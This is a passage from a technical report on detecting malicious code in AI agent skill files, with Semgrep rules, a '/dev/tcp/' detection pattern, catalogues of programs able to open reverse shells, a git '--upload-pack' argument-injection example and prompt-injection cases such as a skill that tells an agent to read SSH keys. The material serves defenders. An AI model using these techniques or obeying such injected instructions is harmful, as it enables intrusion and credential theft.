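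| Code block in SKILL.md | the skill's author | often the language, and anything set up in other blocks |
| Notebook cell | a document that mixes text with code that people run piece by piece | imports and variables from earlier cells |
| Change to a file | the agent's editing tool | the rest of the file |
| Program in a string | an argument to an interpreter, as in `python3 -c "…"` | a file of its own |

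Some of this text may never be in a file on the user's machine. *SkillGate* (Yang, Fu and colleagues, 2026) describes a filter for skills and notes that a tool server can deliver a skill's content in its replies, which go straight into the model's context.

A scanner has four problems with snippets. The language may be unknown, and the text may not parse. The lines that a rule requires around a suspicious call may be outside the snippet. One language may also be nested in another, and a parser for the outer language then treats the inner program as an ordinary string.

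### From a code block to a finding

Suppose the sales-report skill's SKILL.md has a code block labelled `bash`, with these commands on lines 21 and 22:

```
pip install openpyxl
python3 -c "import pickle; pickle.load(open('totals.pkl', 'rb'))"
```

The second command passes a short Python program to the interpreter as a string. The pickle-load rule should match that program, but Semgrep doesn't apply Python rules to Markdown files. A pipeline around the scanner can solve this.

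The pipeline first extracts the block and stores the number of its first line, 21. If the block is inside a bulleted list, the pipeline must remove the extra indentation, which would be an error in Python.

The pipeline next identifies the language. Here the label `bash` gives it, but authors often leave labels out. Without one, the pipeline can look for an interpreter on the first line, a familiar command or a keyword such as `import`. Trying parsers until one accepts the text is less reliable, because the shell command `ls` is also a valid Python expression.

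The pipeline then writes the text to a temporary file called `snippet-21.sh`, because the scanner uses the extension to choose a parser. Semgrep's tool server, which lets an agent request a scan, also takes a filename with the code. In its example call, a program sends the name `hello_world.py` and the file's contents. Some rules apply only to certain paths. A rule limited to `.vscode/tasks.json` won't run on `snippet-21.sh`, so the temporary folder should reproduce the original path of any configuration file.

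The scanner can now run its Bash rules. They can match the call to `python3`, but they treat the Python program only as an argument. The pipeline therefore looks for interpreters that accept a program as a string, removes the quotes, and repeats the earlier steps with a second file, `snippet-22.py`. The pickle-load rule matches this file.

The text left after removing the quotes may differ from the program that runs. Inside double quotes, the shell replaces variables like `$TARGET` before Python starts. Code can also be nested in several layers, such as Python inside a shell command inside a JSON file, so the pipeline needs a maximum depth and should record anything deeper as not analysed.

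Teams will probably have to write this extraction step themselves. Semgrep's documentation mentions an experimental extract mode for files that mix languages, but the link to it leads to a page of deprecated experiments. The documentation also suggests generic patterns as a simpler alternative.

Generic rules, which match text without parsing it, are the pipeline's fallback. They should run on the original SKILL.md as well as the snippets, so that they also cover commands in the middle of a sentence, which the pipeline doesn't extract.

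The pipeline then maps each finding back to its place in the original file. The pickle-load finding is on line 1 of `snippet-22.py`, which is line 22 of SKILL.md. For a finding in `snippet-21.sh`, the pipeline adds 20 to the line number. A JSON file can hold a whole program on one line, with `\n` for each line break, so a finding there should also include the JSON key. If a generic rule also flagged the same call, the pipeline merges the two findings.

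When a snippet is a change to an existing file and that file is available, the pipeline can apply the change to a copy and scan the whole copy, which restores the missing context. Comparing the findings before and after the change is safer than keeping only those on changed lines, because an import added at the top of a file can complete a match on a call that was already there.

### When the text does not parse

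Snippets often fail to parse for innocent reasons. A change may start in the middle of a function. Documentation contains placeholders such as `<your-file>`, and Bash treats the angle brackets as redirections. A Python notebook can contain `%pip install`, a notebook command that is not valid Python, or a cell that begins with `%%bash` and contains shell code.

A wrong parse can do more damage than a failed one because it produces no error. Many authors include the shell prompt in their documentation, as in `$ npm install`. Bash treats the lone dollar sign as the command name and `npm` as its first argument, so a rule for the command `npm` can miss the line. The pipeline can remove the prompt before scanning, but it should record the change because the scanned text then differs slightly from what the author wrote.

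If a snippet still doesn't parse, the pipeline should record it as "not analysed" rather than "clean", even if the generic rules found nothing. Trail of Bits' *Semgrep Security Scan*, a skill for running Semgrep through an agent, applies this principle to whole codebases. Its instructions to the agent include the warning that "a partial scan presented as a complete one is worse than no scan." Its script lists the scans that ran, failed, were skipped or covered no files. The final report must also name files above the size limit and scans in which some rules didn't compile.

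Whatever acts on the scan result must also be able to distinguish a parse error from a clean scan. If a PreToolUse script returns nothing after a parse error, the effect is the same as a clean scan, and Claude Code's normal permission process may already allow the command. The script should instead ask the user to approve the command.

### An import in an earlier cell

Missing context is harder to notice because the snippet parses and the scan finishes normally. This rule looks for Python programs that can use the network and also start another program:

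```
rules:
  - id: network-and-process
    languages: [python]
    severity: INFO
    message: This code imports socket and starts $PROGRAM.
    patterns:
      - pattern-inside: |
          import socket
          ...
      - pattern: subprocess.call([$PROGRAM, ...])
```

A notebook might have the imports in its first cell:

```
import socket
import subprocess
```

and the call in its second:

```
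subprocess.call(["sh", "backup.sh"])
```

If the pipeline scans each cell separately, the rule finds nothing, because the import is in the first cell and the call is in the second. The Semgrep registry's rule for Python reverse shells also requires `import socket` before the call, so it has the same weakness.

The pipeline can fix this by joining the cells into one file before scanning. Alternatively, the rule writer can drop the rule's import condition or add a generic rule with the pattern `subprocess.call(...)`. The table compares the results on six invented cases. The last column shows whether the code actually imports `socket` and starts a program, which is what the rule is meant to find.

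| Case | Cells or blocks joined | Relaxed rule | Generic rule | Should match |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Import in one cell, call in the next | match | match | match | yes |
| The same, but with `import subprocess as sp` and `sp.call(…)` | match | no match | no match | yes |
| The same as the first, but the parser rejects the second cell | not analysed | not analysed | match | yes |
| Call in a notebook that never imports `socket` | no match | match | match | no |
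| Import and call in two unrelated examples in SKILL.md | match | match | match | no |
| Import in one cell, call only in a comment in the next | no match | no match | match | no |

Joining gives one false alarm here, the relaxed rule gives two, and the generic rule gives three. The cases are few and were chosen deliberately, so they show what causes each problem but not how common it is.

Joining is the only remedy that handles the second case, because Semgrep can work out that `sp` means `subprocess` only if the import is in the file it scans. But joining can create a program nobody would run, as with the two unrelated examples in SKILL.md. One faulty cell can also prevent the scanner from parsing the whole joined file, so the pipeline should scan the cells separately as well. People can run notebook cells in any order, so the import may come after the call in the document, and then this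 rule won't match the joined file.

Relaxing the rule is the easiest change and doesn't require other cells, so it also works on single commands and strings. But the relaxed rule flags any ordinary script that starts a program this way. Its message also has to change, since a match is no longer evidence of network access.

Only the generic rule works on the cell that doesn't parse, but it also matches comments and quoted examples. Trail of Bits recommends limiting the rule to certain paths, which works less well for skills because their documentation also needs checking.

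For notebooks, joining the cells is the best default because they normally share variables and imports. For SKILL.md, it's safer to join only code blocks that are in the same language and under the same heading. The generic rule can run on everything, as long as its findings are low severity.

### CodeShield

CodeShield is Meta's scanner for code written by language models. It accepts Semgrep rules and regular expressions, and is now part of LlamaFirewall, an open-source set of checks for AI agents. *LlamaFirewall* (Chennabasappa, Nikolaidis and colleagues, 2025) gives an example in which an agent copies an unsafe database query from a popular web post. CodeShield scans the change and rejects it, and the agent rewrites the query until it passes the scan.

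CodeShield scans code in two stages to keep delays short. The first uses light pattern matching and static analysis and takes about 60 milliseconds. If it flags a possible problem, a more thorough second stage runs, averaging about 300 milliseconds. In Meta's own use, as of April 2025, about 90% of inputs needed only the first stage. This makes it practical to scan every piece of code an agent writes. But because the second stage examines only flagged code, it can remove false alarms but can't catch anything the first stage missed.

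Chennabasappa and colleagues report a precision of 96% and a recall of 79%, citing a 2024 evaluation, but *Purple Llama CyberSecEval* (2023) had already reported the same figures for the Insecure Code Detector, the library that CodeShield is built on. For that 2023 paper, researchers hand-labelled 50 model-written completions per language as secure or insecure and compared the labels with the detector's results. At 79% recall, the detector misses about one insecure completion in five. The test is nearly three years old, and both the rules and the models have probably changed since.

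*Static Analysis Guidance for Secure LLM Code Generation* (2026), a newer study using other tests, is much less favourable to static analysis in general. It compared analysers' flags with independent checks of whether working, model-written programs were insecure. In one of its benchmarks, BaxBench, a program counts as insecure if an exploit against it succeeds. The study concludes that static analysis detects only a small part of the insecurity and that its flags are "barely more likely than chance" to mark insecure code. Recall reached 80% to 94% on the RiskyPy benchmark, but its designers had chosen the tasks because analysers flag their solutions. CodeShield's 79% may also depend on the tasks in its test, so a team shouldn't assume the same recall on its own code.

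All of these figures are about insecure code, which has a flaw that someone else could exploit. Malicious code does harm by design and may have no such flaw. A rule against passing unchecked input to a shell could also match some reverse shells, but a working reverse shell that contains no typical programming mistake could pass a pack of rules for insecure code.

Meta's documents are a little ambiguous about whether CodeShield covers malicious code. The *CodeShield* page lists malicious code that results from prompt injection (hostile instructions hidden in text the model reads) among the risks covered, but only "in conjunction with other scanners". Chennabasappa and colleagues list malicious code execution among the threats that LlamaFirewall will cover in future. CodeShield accepts rules in Semgrep's format, so a team could add rules for reverse shells, but it would have to measure their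 precision and recall itself.

### Scanning inside a coding agent

Semgrep can scan code while an agent works, either through a tool server or through a hook that starts a scan automatically. The server gives the agent scanning tools, including one that accepts a custom rule, so a team can supply its own reverse-shell rules. Semgrep first published the server separately, then moved it into the main program in October 2025. Semgrep Guardian combines the server, hooks and skills in one installation.

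The difference matters because a tool runs only if the agent calls it. The server's original documentation advised Cursor users to add an instruction to always scan generated code, but a model can fail to follow it. According to Semgrep's setup guide, Guardian uses hooks in Claude Code, Cursor and Windsurf. VS Code and GitHub Copilot have no hook that runs after a file is written, so there Guardian depends on the agent to request a scan. The July 2026 version of the guide described Codex the same way, but Semgrep now recommends a plugin for it.

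Guardian scans new code after a write or an edit, when the code is already on disk. Semgrep explains that Guardian returns any findings to the agent, which decides whether to rewrite the code. This makes sense for accidental flaws, which the model can usually correct. It's a weaker defence against malicious code, because the model may have written that code to follow a hostile instruction in its context. The scan also doesn't cover one-line commands sent straight to the shell, since they aren't file edits, but a PreToolUse check does.

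Anthropic's *Catch security issues as Claude writes code* describes the company's security-guidance plugin, which runs a text match whenever Claude edits a file or a notebook. The match looks for risky calls such as `eval(` and `os.system`, and for changes to automated GitHub jobs. It needs no model, and it works on fragments because it doesn't parse the new text. Separate model reviews run at the end of each turn and when Claude commits code. The end-of-turn review also covers changes that shell commands made to files, and the commit review also reads related code for context that a snippet lacks. None of the three checks can block a change.

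Users can add up to 50 patterns to the text match. This one would warn about Bash's network path:

```
patterns:
  - rule_name: bash_network_path
    substrings: ["/dev/tcp/"]
    reminder: "This text has a Bash network path. Check its purpose."
```

This check can miss a match in two ways without any message in the conversation. If the computer lacks PyYAML, a Python library for reading YAML, the plugin ignores the whole pattern file, so Anthropic recommends JSON in that case. Each warning also appears only once per pattern, file and session, so a second network path in the same file would produce no warning, even if the first was harmless.

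The products also differ in what they look for:

| Check | Main targets | Result of a finding |
|---|---|---|
| CodeShield | insecure code | the application can reject the code |
| Semgrep Guardian | insecure code, risky packages, exposed passwords and keys | the agent decides whether to rewrite the code |
| Anthropic's security-guidance | risky calls and common vulnerabilities | Claude receives a warning or review comments |
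| Semgrep's Agent Skills rules | malicious patterns in skill files | depends on how the team runs the rules |

The last row is the closest to a pack for malicious code. Semgrep lists 122 commercial rules for malicious patterns in skill definitions separately from Guardian, and says they cover credential access, command execution, persistence and data theft. Another new pack has 186 rules that mostly find where a codebase uses language models, which is useful for an inventory but not for detecting attacks. Guardian's remote and local versions also use different rules, so a team should check which packs its installation loads. A simple test is to scan a harmless file that one of the malicious-code rules should match.

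### What the snippet does not contain

Even a perfect pipeline can scan only the text it receives. If a command downloads a script, the pipeline could fetch and scan that script too, but the server might send something different later.

Values that exist only at run time cause a similar problem. In `python3 "$SCRIPT"`, the snippet doesn't show which file will run, and in `/dev/tcp/$host/$port` it doesn't show where the connection goes. If an earlier command set the variable, the pipeline may be able to recover its value by joining the commands, but it can't recover a value that comes from a server or the user's environment. The rule can still report the call, and the message should mark the target as unknown.

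A SKILL.md file could contain no code and still tell the agent in plain language to read the user's SSH keys and include them in a report, leaving the agent to choose the commands. Semgrep can search any text, including these files, and now sells rules for them. Yang and colleagues therefore go too far when they argue that such files bypass tools like Semgrep because those tools examine source code. But a text rule matches only particular wording, and the file's author can phrase the same request in many ways.

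A rule can also match words that are there for a legitimate reason. Aguirre (2026), in *AI Agent Skills*, describes a prompt injection rule that matched "Ignore previous instructions" in a skill for managing email, where the sentence was an example in a warning about that attack. Aguirre added a language model to review the flagged results, and it removed most such false positives.

SkillGate also combines rules with a model, using the rules to choose snippets. It searches a skill file with 530 regular expressions, then sends the model up to 500 characters on each side of every match, along with the skill's name and file path. This context can be enough to distinguish a warning from an instruction. But the excerpts are limited to 8,000 characters in total, which fits only seven at full size, so the model may not receive every match in a long file. By default, SkillGate labels files with no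 matches safe without sending them to the model, even if they contain a harmful instruction whose wording the expressions don't cover. Teams can change this setting so that the model reviews every file, at a higher cost.

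## Why coverage of living-off-the-land binaries stays incomplete

A rule pack can grow for years and still miss attacks that use LOLBins. How large the gap looks depends on what "coverage" means. People use the word for three different shares:

- the catalogued programs for which the pack has a rule
- the known techniques for which it has a rule, since one program can often do the same harm in several ways
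- the actual misuse that the pack catches, which is its recall

The April 2026 copy of GTFOBins lists 21 programs that can open a reverse shell, not counting aliases. Of these, 12 (57%) appear in the 19 reverse-shell rules in Ansible Security Scanner.

| Rule in the pack | Programs |
|---|---|
| Yes, by name | bash, gawk, lua, nc, node, openssl, perl, php, python, ruby, socat, telnet |
| Perhaps, through a related rule | busybox, jjs, jrunscript |
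| No | code, go, julia, socket, tclsh, zsh |

BusyBox combines many small tools in one program, including a version of netcat, so the pack's netcat rule may match it. The programs jjs and jrunscript run JavaScript that can use Java classes, so the Java rule may match them. If the rules match all three programs, coverage rises to 71%. A second pack could fill other gaps. For example, Elastic's terminal rule looks for zsh's network modules, although it reads process logs rather than files.

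The GTFOBins catalogue is also incomplete. It doesn't list xterm or PowerShell as able to open a reverse shell, though the Ansible pack has rules for both. *Robust Synthetic Data-Driven Detection of Living-Off-the-Land Reverse Shells* (Trizna, Demetrio and colleagues, 2024) cites research that found at least 30 suitable Linux programs, so the total needed to calculate coverage is uncertain.

Techniques are harder to count than programs because no list of techniques is complete. A single rule for the netcat option that runs a program is enough to count netcat as covered, even though the rule misses reverse shells that connect netcat to a shell through a named pipe.

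Recall, the share of attacks that a rule pack catches, can differ greatly from the share of programs it covers. Suppose attackers use Bash, Python or netcat in 90 of 100 attacks, and a pack has rules for only those three programs. It covers 3 of the 21 programs, or 14%. If its rules recognise the forms used in 80% of those 90 attacks, it catches 72 of the 100. A pack with one narrow rule for each of the 21 programs would cover them all but could catch far fewer attacks. Nobody can calculate actual recall exactly, because that would require counting the attacks that no one noticed.

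There are six reasons to expect gaps, and some are much easier to fix than others.

### Programs that no catalogue lists yet

Catalogues such as LOLBAS depend on volunteers to find new entries, and volunteers can miss many of them. Researchers at the security company Pentera looked for Windows programs that can download a file but were not yet in LOLBAS. They began by manually testing the programs in the Microsoft Office folder, running each with a web address as its only argument and watching their own web server for a request. Within two hours they had found three downloaders.

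Windows contains more than 3,000 executable files, so the researchers then automated the test and found six more downloaders, for a total of nine. They describe the nine as almost a 30% increase in LOLBAS's list of downloaders, which implies that the list previously had a little over 30.

The researchers also searched for programs that can start another program. This time they used a small test file as the argument, which logged the name of its parent process when it ran, and combined it with every single-letter option in upper and lower case. They found three more programs: scp, sftp and an Office component called MsoHtmEd.

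This is a company's account of its own work, but the method is simple enough for others to repeat. The method probably undercounts, because the download test gave each program only an address and would miss any program that also needs a particular option or settings file to download.

A defender who ran the same search and wrote 12 more rules could nearly finish covering the 3,000 programs in one version of Windows, but those rules would not cover third-party software. LOLBAS accepts only files signed by Microsoft, and Pentera points out that attackers could in theory use Zoom, Slack or the code editor PyCharm in the same way. New software also keeps arriving. GTFOBins now has entries for two coding agents, Codex and OpenCode, because each can start other commands.

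### One effect, many spellings

Even for a well-known program, a rule can miss a different way of writing the same command. *Democratizing ML for Enterprise Security* (Momeni, Zhang and colleagues, 2025) describes this problem from experience at Google. It compares two commands that use Bash's network path, one that opens a reverse shell and one that only tests whether a port is open. An engineer might notice that only the reverse shell contains the characters `>&` and change the rule to require them. The rule then stops flagging the port test, but it also misses any reverse shell that attaches its streams in separate steps and never uses those two characters together.

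Published rules have the same weakness. Semgrep's Python rule requires `/bin/`, so it would miss the Python example in that paper, which starts the shell as plain `sh`.

Much of the variety in reverse-shell commands is superficial, however. Trizna and colleagues published a dataset of more than a million such commands, which they generated from templates. The parts that vary are the shell, protocol, address, port, stream number, temporary file path and variable names. A metavariable or a short regular expression can match any of these, so one rule can cover many variants.

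The differences between templates are harder to cover. In GTFOBins, the example for jjs starts a process, opens a socket and copies data between them in a loop. Semgrep's rule for Java reverse shells looks for nearly the same calls in nearly the same order, but a scanner wouldn't apply it to this file because jjs runs JavaScript.

### Programs that run other programs

Some programs cannot open a reverse shell with their own features but can run code in a language that can. GTFOBins records this with its "inherit" function. In the catalogue, 37 programs inherit directly from one of the 21 that can open a reverse shell.

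| Language | Programs that can run it | Examples |
|---|---|---|
| Python | 12 | the debugger gdb, the package installer pip |
| Lua | 11 | the network scanner nmap, the document converter pandoc |
| Ruby | 7 | rake, which runs build tasks |
| Perl | 6 | exiftool, which reads data stored in photos |
| PHP | 1 | bee, which manages websites |
| Tcl | 1 | wish, which runs programs with windows |

The numbers add up to 38 because the text editor Vim can run both Python and Lua. Inheritance can also take more than one step, as when the Ruby console pry inherits from another console, irb, which inherits from Ruby. Two more programs do the same, so the 21 programs become 61 before counting aliases.

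Python code run through gdb makes the same calls as any other Python program, so a scanner that extracts code from commands can treat gdb like `python3 -c` and apply its existing Python rules. If a rule pack has five Python patterns, writing a separate rule for each combination with the 12 launching programs would take 60 rules, while extraction needs only the five patterns and a list of the 12 launchers. Several launchers take the code from a file instead, so the scanner has to open that file too. For example, pip runs the `setup.py` in the folder it installs from.

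A single option can be enough to make a program run another command. In an argument injection attack, the attacker controls only an argument of a command that a program already runs. The code-analysis company SonarSource maintains a catalogue of arguments that can be exploited this way, in a format adapted from GTFOBins. It sorts them by four effects: running a command, reading a file, writing a file and loading a library.

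SonarSource's example is `git ls-remote`, which normally lists the branches and tags of a remote repository. An attacker can put a command in its `--upload-pack` option, which specifies a program for Git to run. A rule that matches the names of shells and network tools could miss this because the line looks like a routine Git query. The Git entry in GTFOBins lists several ways to start a shell but not this one, so a rule writer who used only that catalogue would miss it too.

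A rule for `--upload-pack` is easy to write once someone has documented the option. Finding all such options is much more work, because a tool like Git has many, and new versions can add more.

### When the harmful use is the intended use

VS Code's `code tunnel` command lets a developer work on a computer remotely. It connects the computer to a remote service, and the developer then opens the editor in a browser and can use a terminal there. GTFOBins lists the command as a reverse shell and as a way to upload and download files.

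A developer and an attacker would type the same command to open a VS Code tunnel. The difference is whose GitHub account authorises the connection, and that happens on GitHub's website after the command has started. The script contains no address, shell or redirection, because VS Code supplies all three parts of the reverse shell. A more precise rule can't separate the harmless use from the harmful one, because the text is identical in both.

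The same is true of many downloads and uploads with curl, wget or scp, where only the address may differ.

A defender doesn't always have to tell legitimate use from malicious use. A team that never uses VS Code tunnels can block the command in every skill as a matter of policy, whatever the skill's author intended. A false alarm then does little harm, because the team has no ordinary use to interrupt. This works for tunnels because few skills need one, but it would not work for curl, which many skills need.

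### Versions and platforms

Whether a command does harm can depend on the machine it runs on. According to GTFOBins, nmap has an interactive mode that can start a shell, but only in versions 2.02 to 5.21. A technique for abusing the network monitor tcpdump fails on some newer Linux systems because AppArmor, a security feature that restricts individual programs, limits what tcpdump can start.

The same command name can run different programs on different machines. For example, `awk` may run gawk, for which GTFOBins lists a reverse shell, or mawk, for which it lists none. Someone who scans a skill before publication can't know which program the user's machine will run.

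Most of this matters less to a static rule than it may seem, because the rule doesn't have to establish that a command will work. A rule that matches an nmap option removed years ago produces one unnecessary finding, and even that may be useful, because a script containing an obsolete attack deserves a closer look.

A new version of a program causes misses only when it changes how a command is written. For example, the terminal program `screen` can write a log to a file the user chooses. In version 4.05.00 the filename follows `-L`, while version 4.06.02 needs a separate option, `-Logfile`. A rule written for only one version could miss commands written for the other. The remedy, which is tedious but not difficult, is to keep both patterns and check the manual when a new version comes out.

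### Rules too noisy to keep

Full program coverage would be easy to reach with a rule that matches the name of every program in the catalogue. This ordinary setup script shows the result:

```
curl -o data.tar https://example.com/data.tar
tar xf data.tar
cp data/report.csv .
pip install openpyxl
```

All four programs are in GTFOBins, so the scanner would report a finding on every line. A reviewer who saw this on each script would soon stop reading the findings.

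Even a rule for a specific attack can be far too broad. Momeni and colleagues wrote deliberately loose YARA rules for reverse shells. The rules look for combinations such as Bash's network path and the letters `sh`, and at Google they match about 70,000 logged events a day. After further filtering, analysts receive about one ticket every two days.

Authors probably leave common tools out of their packs for this reason, but this is hard to confirm because a missing rule comes with no explanation. The exceptions in Elastic's terminal rule show only that authors exclude individual cases. It is unclear whether the six programs missing from the Ansible pack were left out deliberately or overlooked. For Julia and Tcl, oversight is more likely, because neither is common enough in server configuration for a rule to cause much noise.

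A noisy rule can still be useful if the pack combines it with other evidence, as GuardDog does. This reduces false positives, but it can cause the pack to miss some attacks again, because an attack that shows only one of the required signs gets a lower score.

### Rules for behaviour and lists of permitted commands

Defenders have several alternatives to writing one rule per program. The most direct is to write a rule that describes a class of behaviour. For example, a data-flow rule can follow text from a network connection to any function that starts a process. Sysdig's newer rule does something similar for running programs.

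Data-flow rules handle different spellings well, and they also help with launchers such as gdb if the scanner extracts the code. But they still need lists of which functions read from the network and which start a process, and someone has to extend those lists for each language. A `code tunnel` command also contains no data flow for these rules to trace.

A list of permitted commands blocks everything that isn't on it, including programs that no one has yet catalogued as living-off-the-land binaries. This suits the commands that an agent passes to its shell, because a script can check each one against the list before the command runs.

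An allowlist that permits any command beginning with `git` also permits `git ls-remote` with the option in SonarSource's example. GTFOBins shows that find, tar, npm and pip can also start other commands. The list therefore has to restrict arguments as well as programs, perhaps by allowing only `git ls-remote origin`.

A permitted command can also start a script, as `node scripts/build.js` does, so the defender still needs rules for the script's contents.

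### Detectors that learn from examples

A learned detector is a statistical model trained on labelled examples of harmful and harmless commands. It scores each new command, so it can flag one that no rule covers.

The 2024 work by Trizna and colleagues is an early, well-documented example. They collected harmless commands from a company network of about 50,000 Linux machines, over two hours for training and another two hours a month later for testing. Real attacks were scarce, so experts wrote reverse shell templates and a program filled in the variable parts, partly with values from the company's logs. They used 70% of the templates for training and the rest for testing. The training set had 533,014 different commands and the test set 470,129, about half of them harmless.

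They then trained the same type of model, a combination of many small decision trees, on three versions of the attacks. They set each model's threshold so that it flagged one in 100,000 harmless commands.

| Attacks in the training set | Attacks detected |
|---|---|
| Many generated variants of each template | 99.94% |
| One standard form of each template | 7.12% |
| One standard form, repeated to balance the classes | 7.75% |

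The low figures may be the more useful ones for rule writers. A model trained on one example per technique missed more than 90% of the attacks, and a rule writer who copies one example per program from a catalogue is in much the same position.

The high figure needs more caution. The test set had about 235,000 harmless commands, so a false-positive rate of one in 100,000 amounts to only two or three false alarms. A few unusual scripts in another company could change that rate considerably. The test templates were new to the model, but they came from the same collection and had the same kinds of variable parts. The model could therefore recognise unfamiliar templates of a familiar type, but the test didn't measure how it would do with a method the experts hadn't thought of.

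The network also produced about 12 million events a day. At the same rate, the model would raise up to 120 false alarms daily if it scored every event separately. Trizna and colleagues grouped commands and removed duplicates, so the real number would be lower.

The system that Momeni and colleagues described in December 2025 combines rules with a learned model. Loose YARA rules select events, a model scores them, and analysts investigate those with the highest scores. Their decisions go back into the training data. Google uses it for reverse shells, for known hacking tools and for LOLBins in general. These are the approximate numbers per day for two of the three:

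| Stage | Reverse shells | LOLBins |
|---|---|---|
| Logged events | 250 billion | 6 billion |
| Selected by the YARA rules | 70,000 | 2,000 |
| Selected by the model | 5 | 0.8 |
| Tickets for analysts | 0.48 | 0.15 |

For each type of attack, a language model generated 10,000 harmful and 10,000 harmless examples in about 20 minutes. The reverse-shell model trained on these examples reached an F1 score of 0.95 on a year of investigated tickets, compared with 0.88 for a model trained on examples that an expert had collected by hand over several days. The F1 score combines precision and recall, and a perfect detector scores 1.

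The simplest model, which counts short sequences of words, did as well as models designed to represent the meaning of a command. In one case, a reverse shell was part of a long command for starting a container. The simple model detected the familiar sequence of symbols, while most of the others missed it in the surrounding text. This is encouraging for people who write rules, because short pieces of text apparently carry much of the evidence, and text rules match such pieces.

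The analysts' feedback also made a clear difference. The team used a year of commands from Google's logs to compare a model that never changed with one it retrained every day. The retrained model started the comparison with 180 days of feedback.

| Result | Fixed model | Retrained model |
|---|---|---|
| Attacks found | 43 | 53 |
| False alarms | 107 | 30 |
| Precision | 29% | 64% |

The retrained model found all 43 attacks that the fixed model found, and ten more. A fixed rule pack has the same disadvantage as the fixed model unless its maintainers learn from each false alarm and miss.

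Recall remains unknown here too. The comparison can't include attacks that both models missed, and the model never scores events that the YARA rules drop. The team also sets the threshold partly by how many tickets analysts can handle in a day, so a small number of tickets is weak evidence that few attacks took place. The longer live test, which ran from September 2023 to May 2025, didn't include the LOLBin detector because it was too new.

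Both systems read logged commands, not source files, which limits their use for scanning a skill. By the time a command reaches the log, the shell has replaced variables with their values, so the log may show an address where the script has only `$host`. But the log entry for `python3 report.py` doesn't include the code in that file. Training data made up of such entries contains few comments, function definitions or long scripts. Google's instructions for generating reverse-shell examples specified commands of 10 to 200 characters.

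The closest match in an agent's work is a single command that it is about to run. A team could try a learned detector there, but the variables would still be unexpanded and the team would have to measure the false-positive rate again. A detector that sees only the command cannot distinguish two uses of `code tunnel` with identical text, because it gives them the same score.

### What more rules can fix

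| Reason for the gap | Effect of adding rules |
|---|---|
| Nobody has listed the program | closes the gap for that program, once someone has found it |
| Many spellings | helps a lot if the rules describe behaviour, little if they copy examples |
| Programs that run other programs | helps if the scanner also extracts the inner code |
| Harmful use is the intended use | none, unless the team can ban the command |
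| Versions and platforms | closes most of the gap, with regular upkeep |
| Noise from common tools | makes it worse without a second check |

For the Ansible pack, rules for Go, Julia, Tcl, zsh and the small network tool socket would be a sensible start. All five open a visible connection, so their rules can follow the same design as those for Python or netcat. The sixth missing program, VS Code, needs only a match on `code tunnel`, but each team has to decide whether that match should block a script or just inform the reviewer. With rules for these six, and BusyBox, jjs and jrunscript added by name, the pack would cover all 21 programs. If attackers mostly use Bash and Python, recall might hardly change, and better rules for those two would help more than the nine new ones.

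## Measured misses and false alarms, and what other evidence adds

Researchers measure how many attacks a scanner catches by running it on skills already labelled malicious or benign. Several teams published such tests in 2026, but none reported recall separately for reverse shells, so the results describe malicious skills in general.

### Three scanners and 140 skills

Truong-Le and colleagues tested Microsoft's OSS-Detect-Backdoor, Cisco's Skill Scanner and YARA with a large public collection of rules. They collected 400 malicious and 300 benign skills from three public sources, used 560 to set up the scanners and kept the other 140 (80 malicious and 60 benign) for the test.

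All three tools report alerts rather than a verdict, so the researchers had to decide how many alerts would classify a skill as malicious. They used the 560 skills to set the threshold at six alerts for OSS-Detect-Backdoor, 11 for YARA and one for Cisco's scanner.

| Scanner | Malicious skills flagged | Benign skills flagged | Average alerts, malicious | Average alerts, benign |
|---|---|---|---|---|
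| OSS-Detect-Backdoor | 26 of 80 (0.33) | 17 of 60 (0.28) | 6 | 12 |
| YARA | 73 of 80 (0.91) | 49 of 60 (0.82) | 60 | 106 |
| Cisco's scanner | 73 of 80 (0.91) | 33 of 60 (0.55) | 2.1 | 1.8 |

YARA found as many malicious skills as Cisco's scanner, but only because it flagged nearly every skill. About 60% of the skills it flagged were malicious, compared with 57% of the whole test set, so a match was weak evidence that a skill was malicious.

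OSS-Detect-Backdoor and YARA also raised more alerts on the average benign skill than on the average malicious one. A few large skills probably explain much of this, because more text gives a rule more chances to match. One benign skill set off 814 YARA alerts, while the medians for the two groups were almost equal. The number of alerts is a poor guide to whether a skill is malicious. Among the 560 setup skills, these two scanners raised more alerts on a random malicious skill than on a random benign one only about half the time, no better than chance. Cisco's scanner did so 72% of the time.

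Cisco's scanner had a 55% false-positive rate on only 60 benign skills, so chance alone could plausibly move that rate by ten percentage points. Results from other tests of the same scanner differ by much more than that. Yang and colleagues used 1,500 real benign skills and 150 malicious ones written by hand. *Elementary, My Dear Watson* (Wang, He and colleagues, 2026) used 100 malicious skills recovered from ClawHub's archive and 100 popular benign ones. *SkillSentry* (2026) reports results on the SkillTrustBench benchmark.

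| Test | Setting of Cisco's scanner | Recall | False-positive rate |
|---|---|---|---|
| Truong-Le and colleagues | rules only, any alert | 91% | 55% |
| Truong-Le and colleagues | with a small language model | 85% | 67% |
| Yang and colleagues | rules only, any finding | 82% | 86% |
| Yang and colleagues | rules only, medium severity or above | 47% | 17% |
| Yang and colleagues | rules only, high severity or above | 7% | 1% |
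| Yang and colleagues | with a language model, critical findings only | 18% | 0.7% |
| Wang, He and colleagues | with a language model | 96% | 23% |
| *SkillSentry* | with a language model | 97% | 54% |

Changing the severity threshold alone can cut recall from 82% to 7%. The language model matters too, and adding one doesn't always help. In the test by Truong-Le and colleagues, adding one made both the miss and false-alarm figures worse, although the two settings aren't strictly comparable because the scanner gave its own verdict when the model was on. Each pair of figures therefore applies only to a particular scanner, with particular settings, on a particular test set.

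Scanners also disagree with each other. *After the Party* (Xiong and Zhang, 2026) compared the three results that ClawHub stores for each skill, from VirusTotal, a static scanner and a language model. The results differed for 23,702 of 61,990 skills, or 38%. Two reviewers with security experience then labelled 180 skills without seeing the scanners' results. Against those labels, the scanners' recall ranged from 22% to 61%.

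These recall figures are low partly because the reviewers flagged anything that deserved a human check, including privacy and financial risks. A malware scanner isn't necessarily wrong to pass a skill flagged for those reasons. The figures also apply only to 276 skills whose archived files exactly matched the listed version. Still, the disagreement is too large for a team to assume that any one of ClawHub's results, or a majority vote, is correct.

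### Attacks that leave little to match

A single recall figure hides large differences between types of attack. Chen, Ji and colleagues (2026), in *SkillsMetric*, tested their own static scanner on 2,000 benign skills and 266 malicious ones covering 16 types. They made 199 of the malicious skills by inserting attacks into real benign skills and wrote the rest themselves. The scanner caught 62% overall. These are some of the results by type:

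| Attack | Samples | Detected |
|---|---|---|
| Sending data to an outsider | 28 | 93% |
| Dangerous command in plain text | 29 | 83% |
| Persistence, for example through a scheduled job or Git hook | 11 | 64% |
| Prompt injection | 12 | 42% |
| Downloading and running a remote script | 29 | 28% |
| Changing the environment, for example PATH | 9 | 22% |
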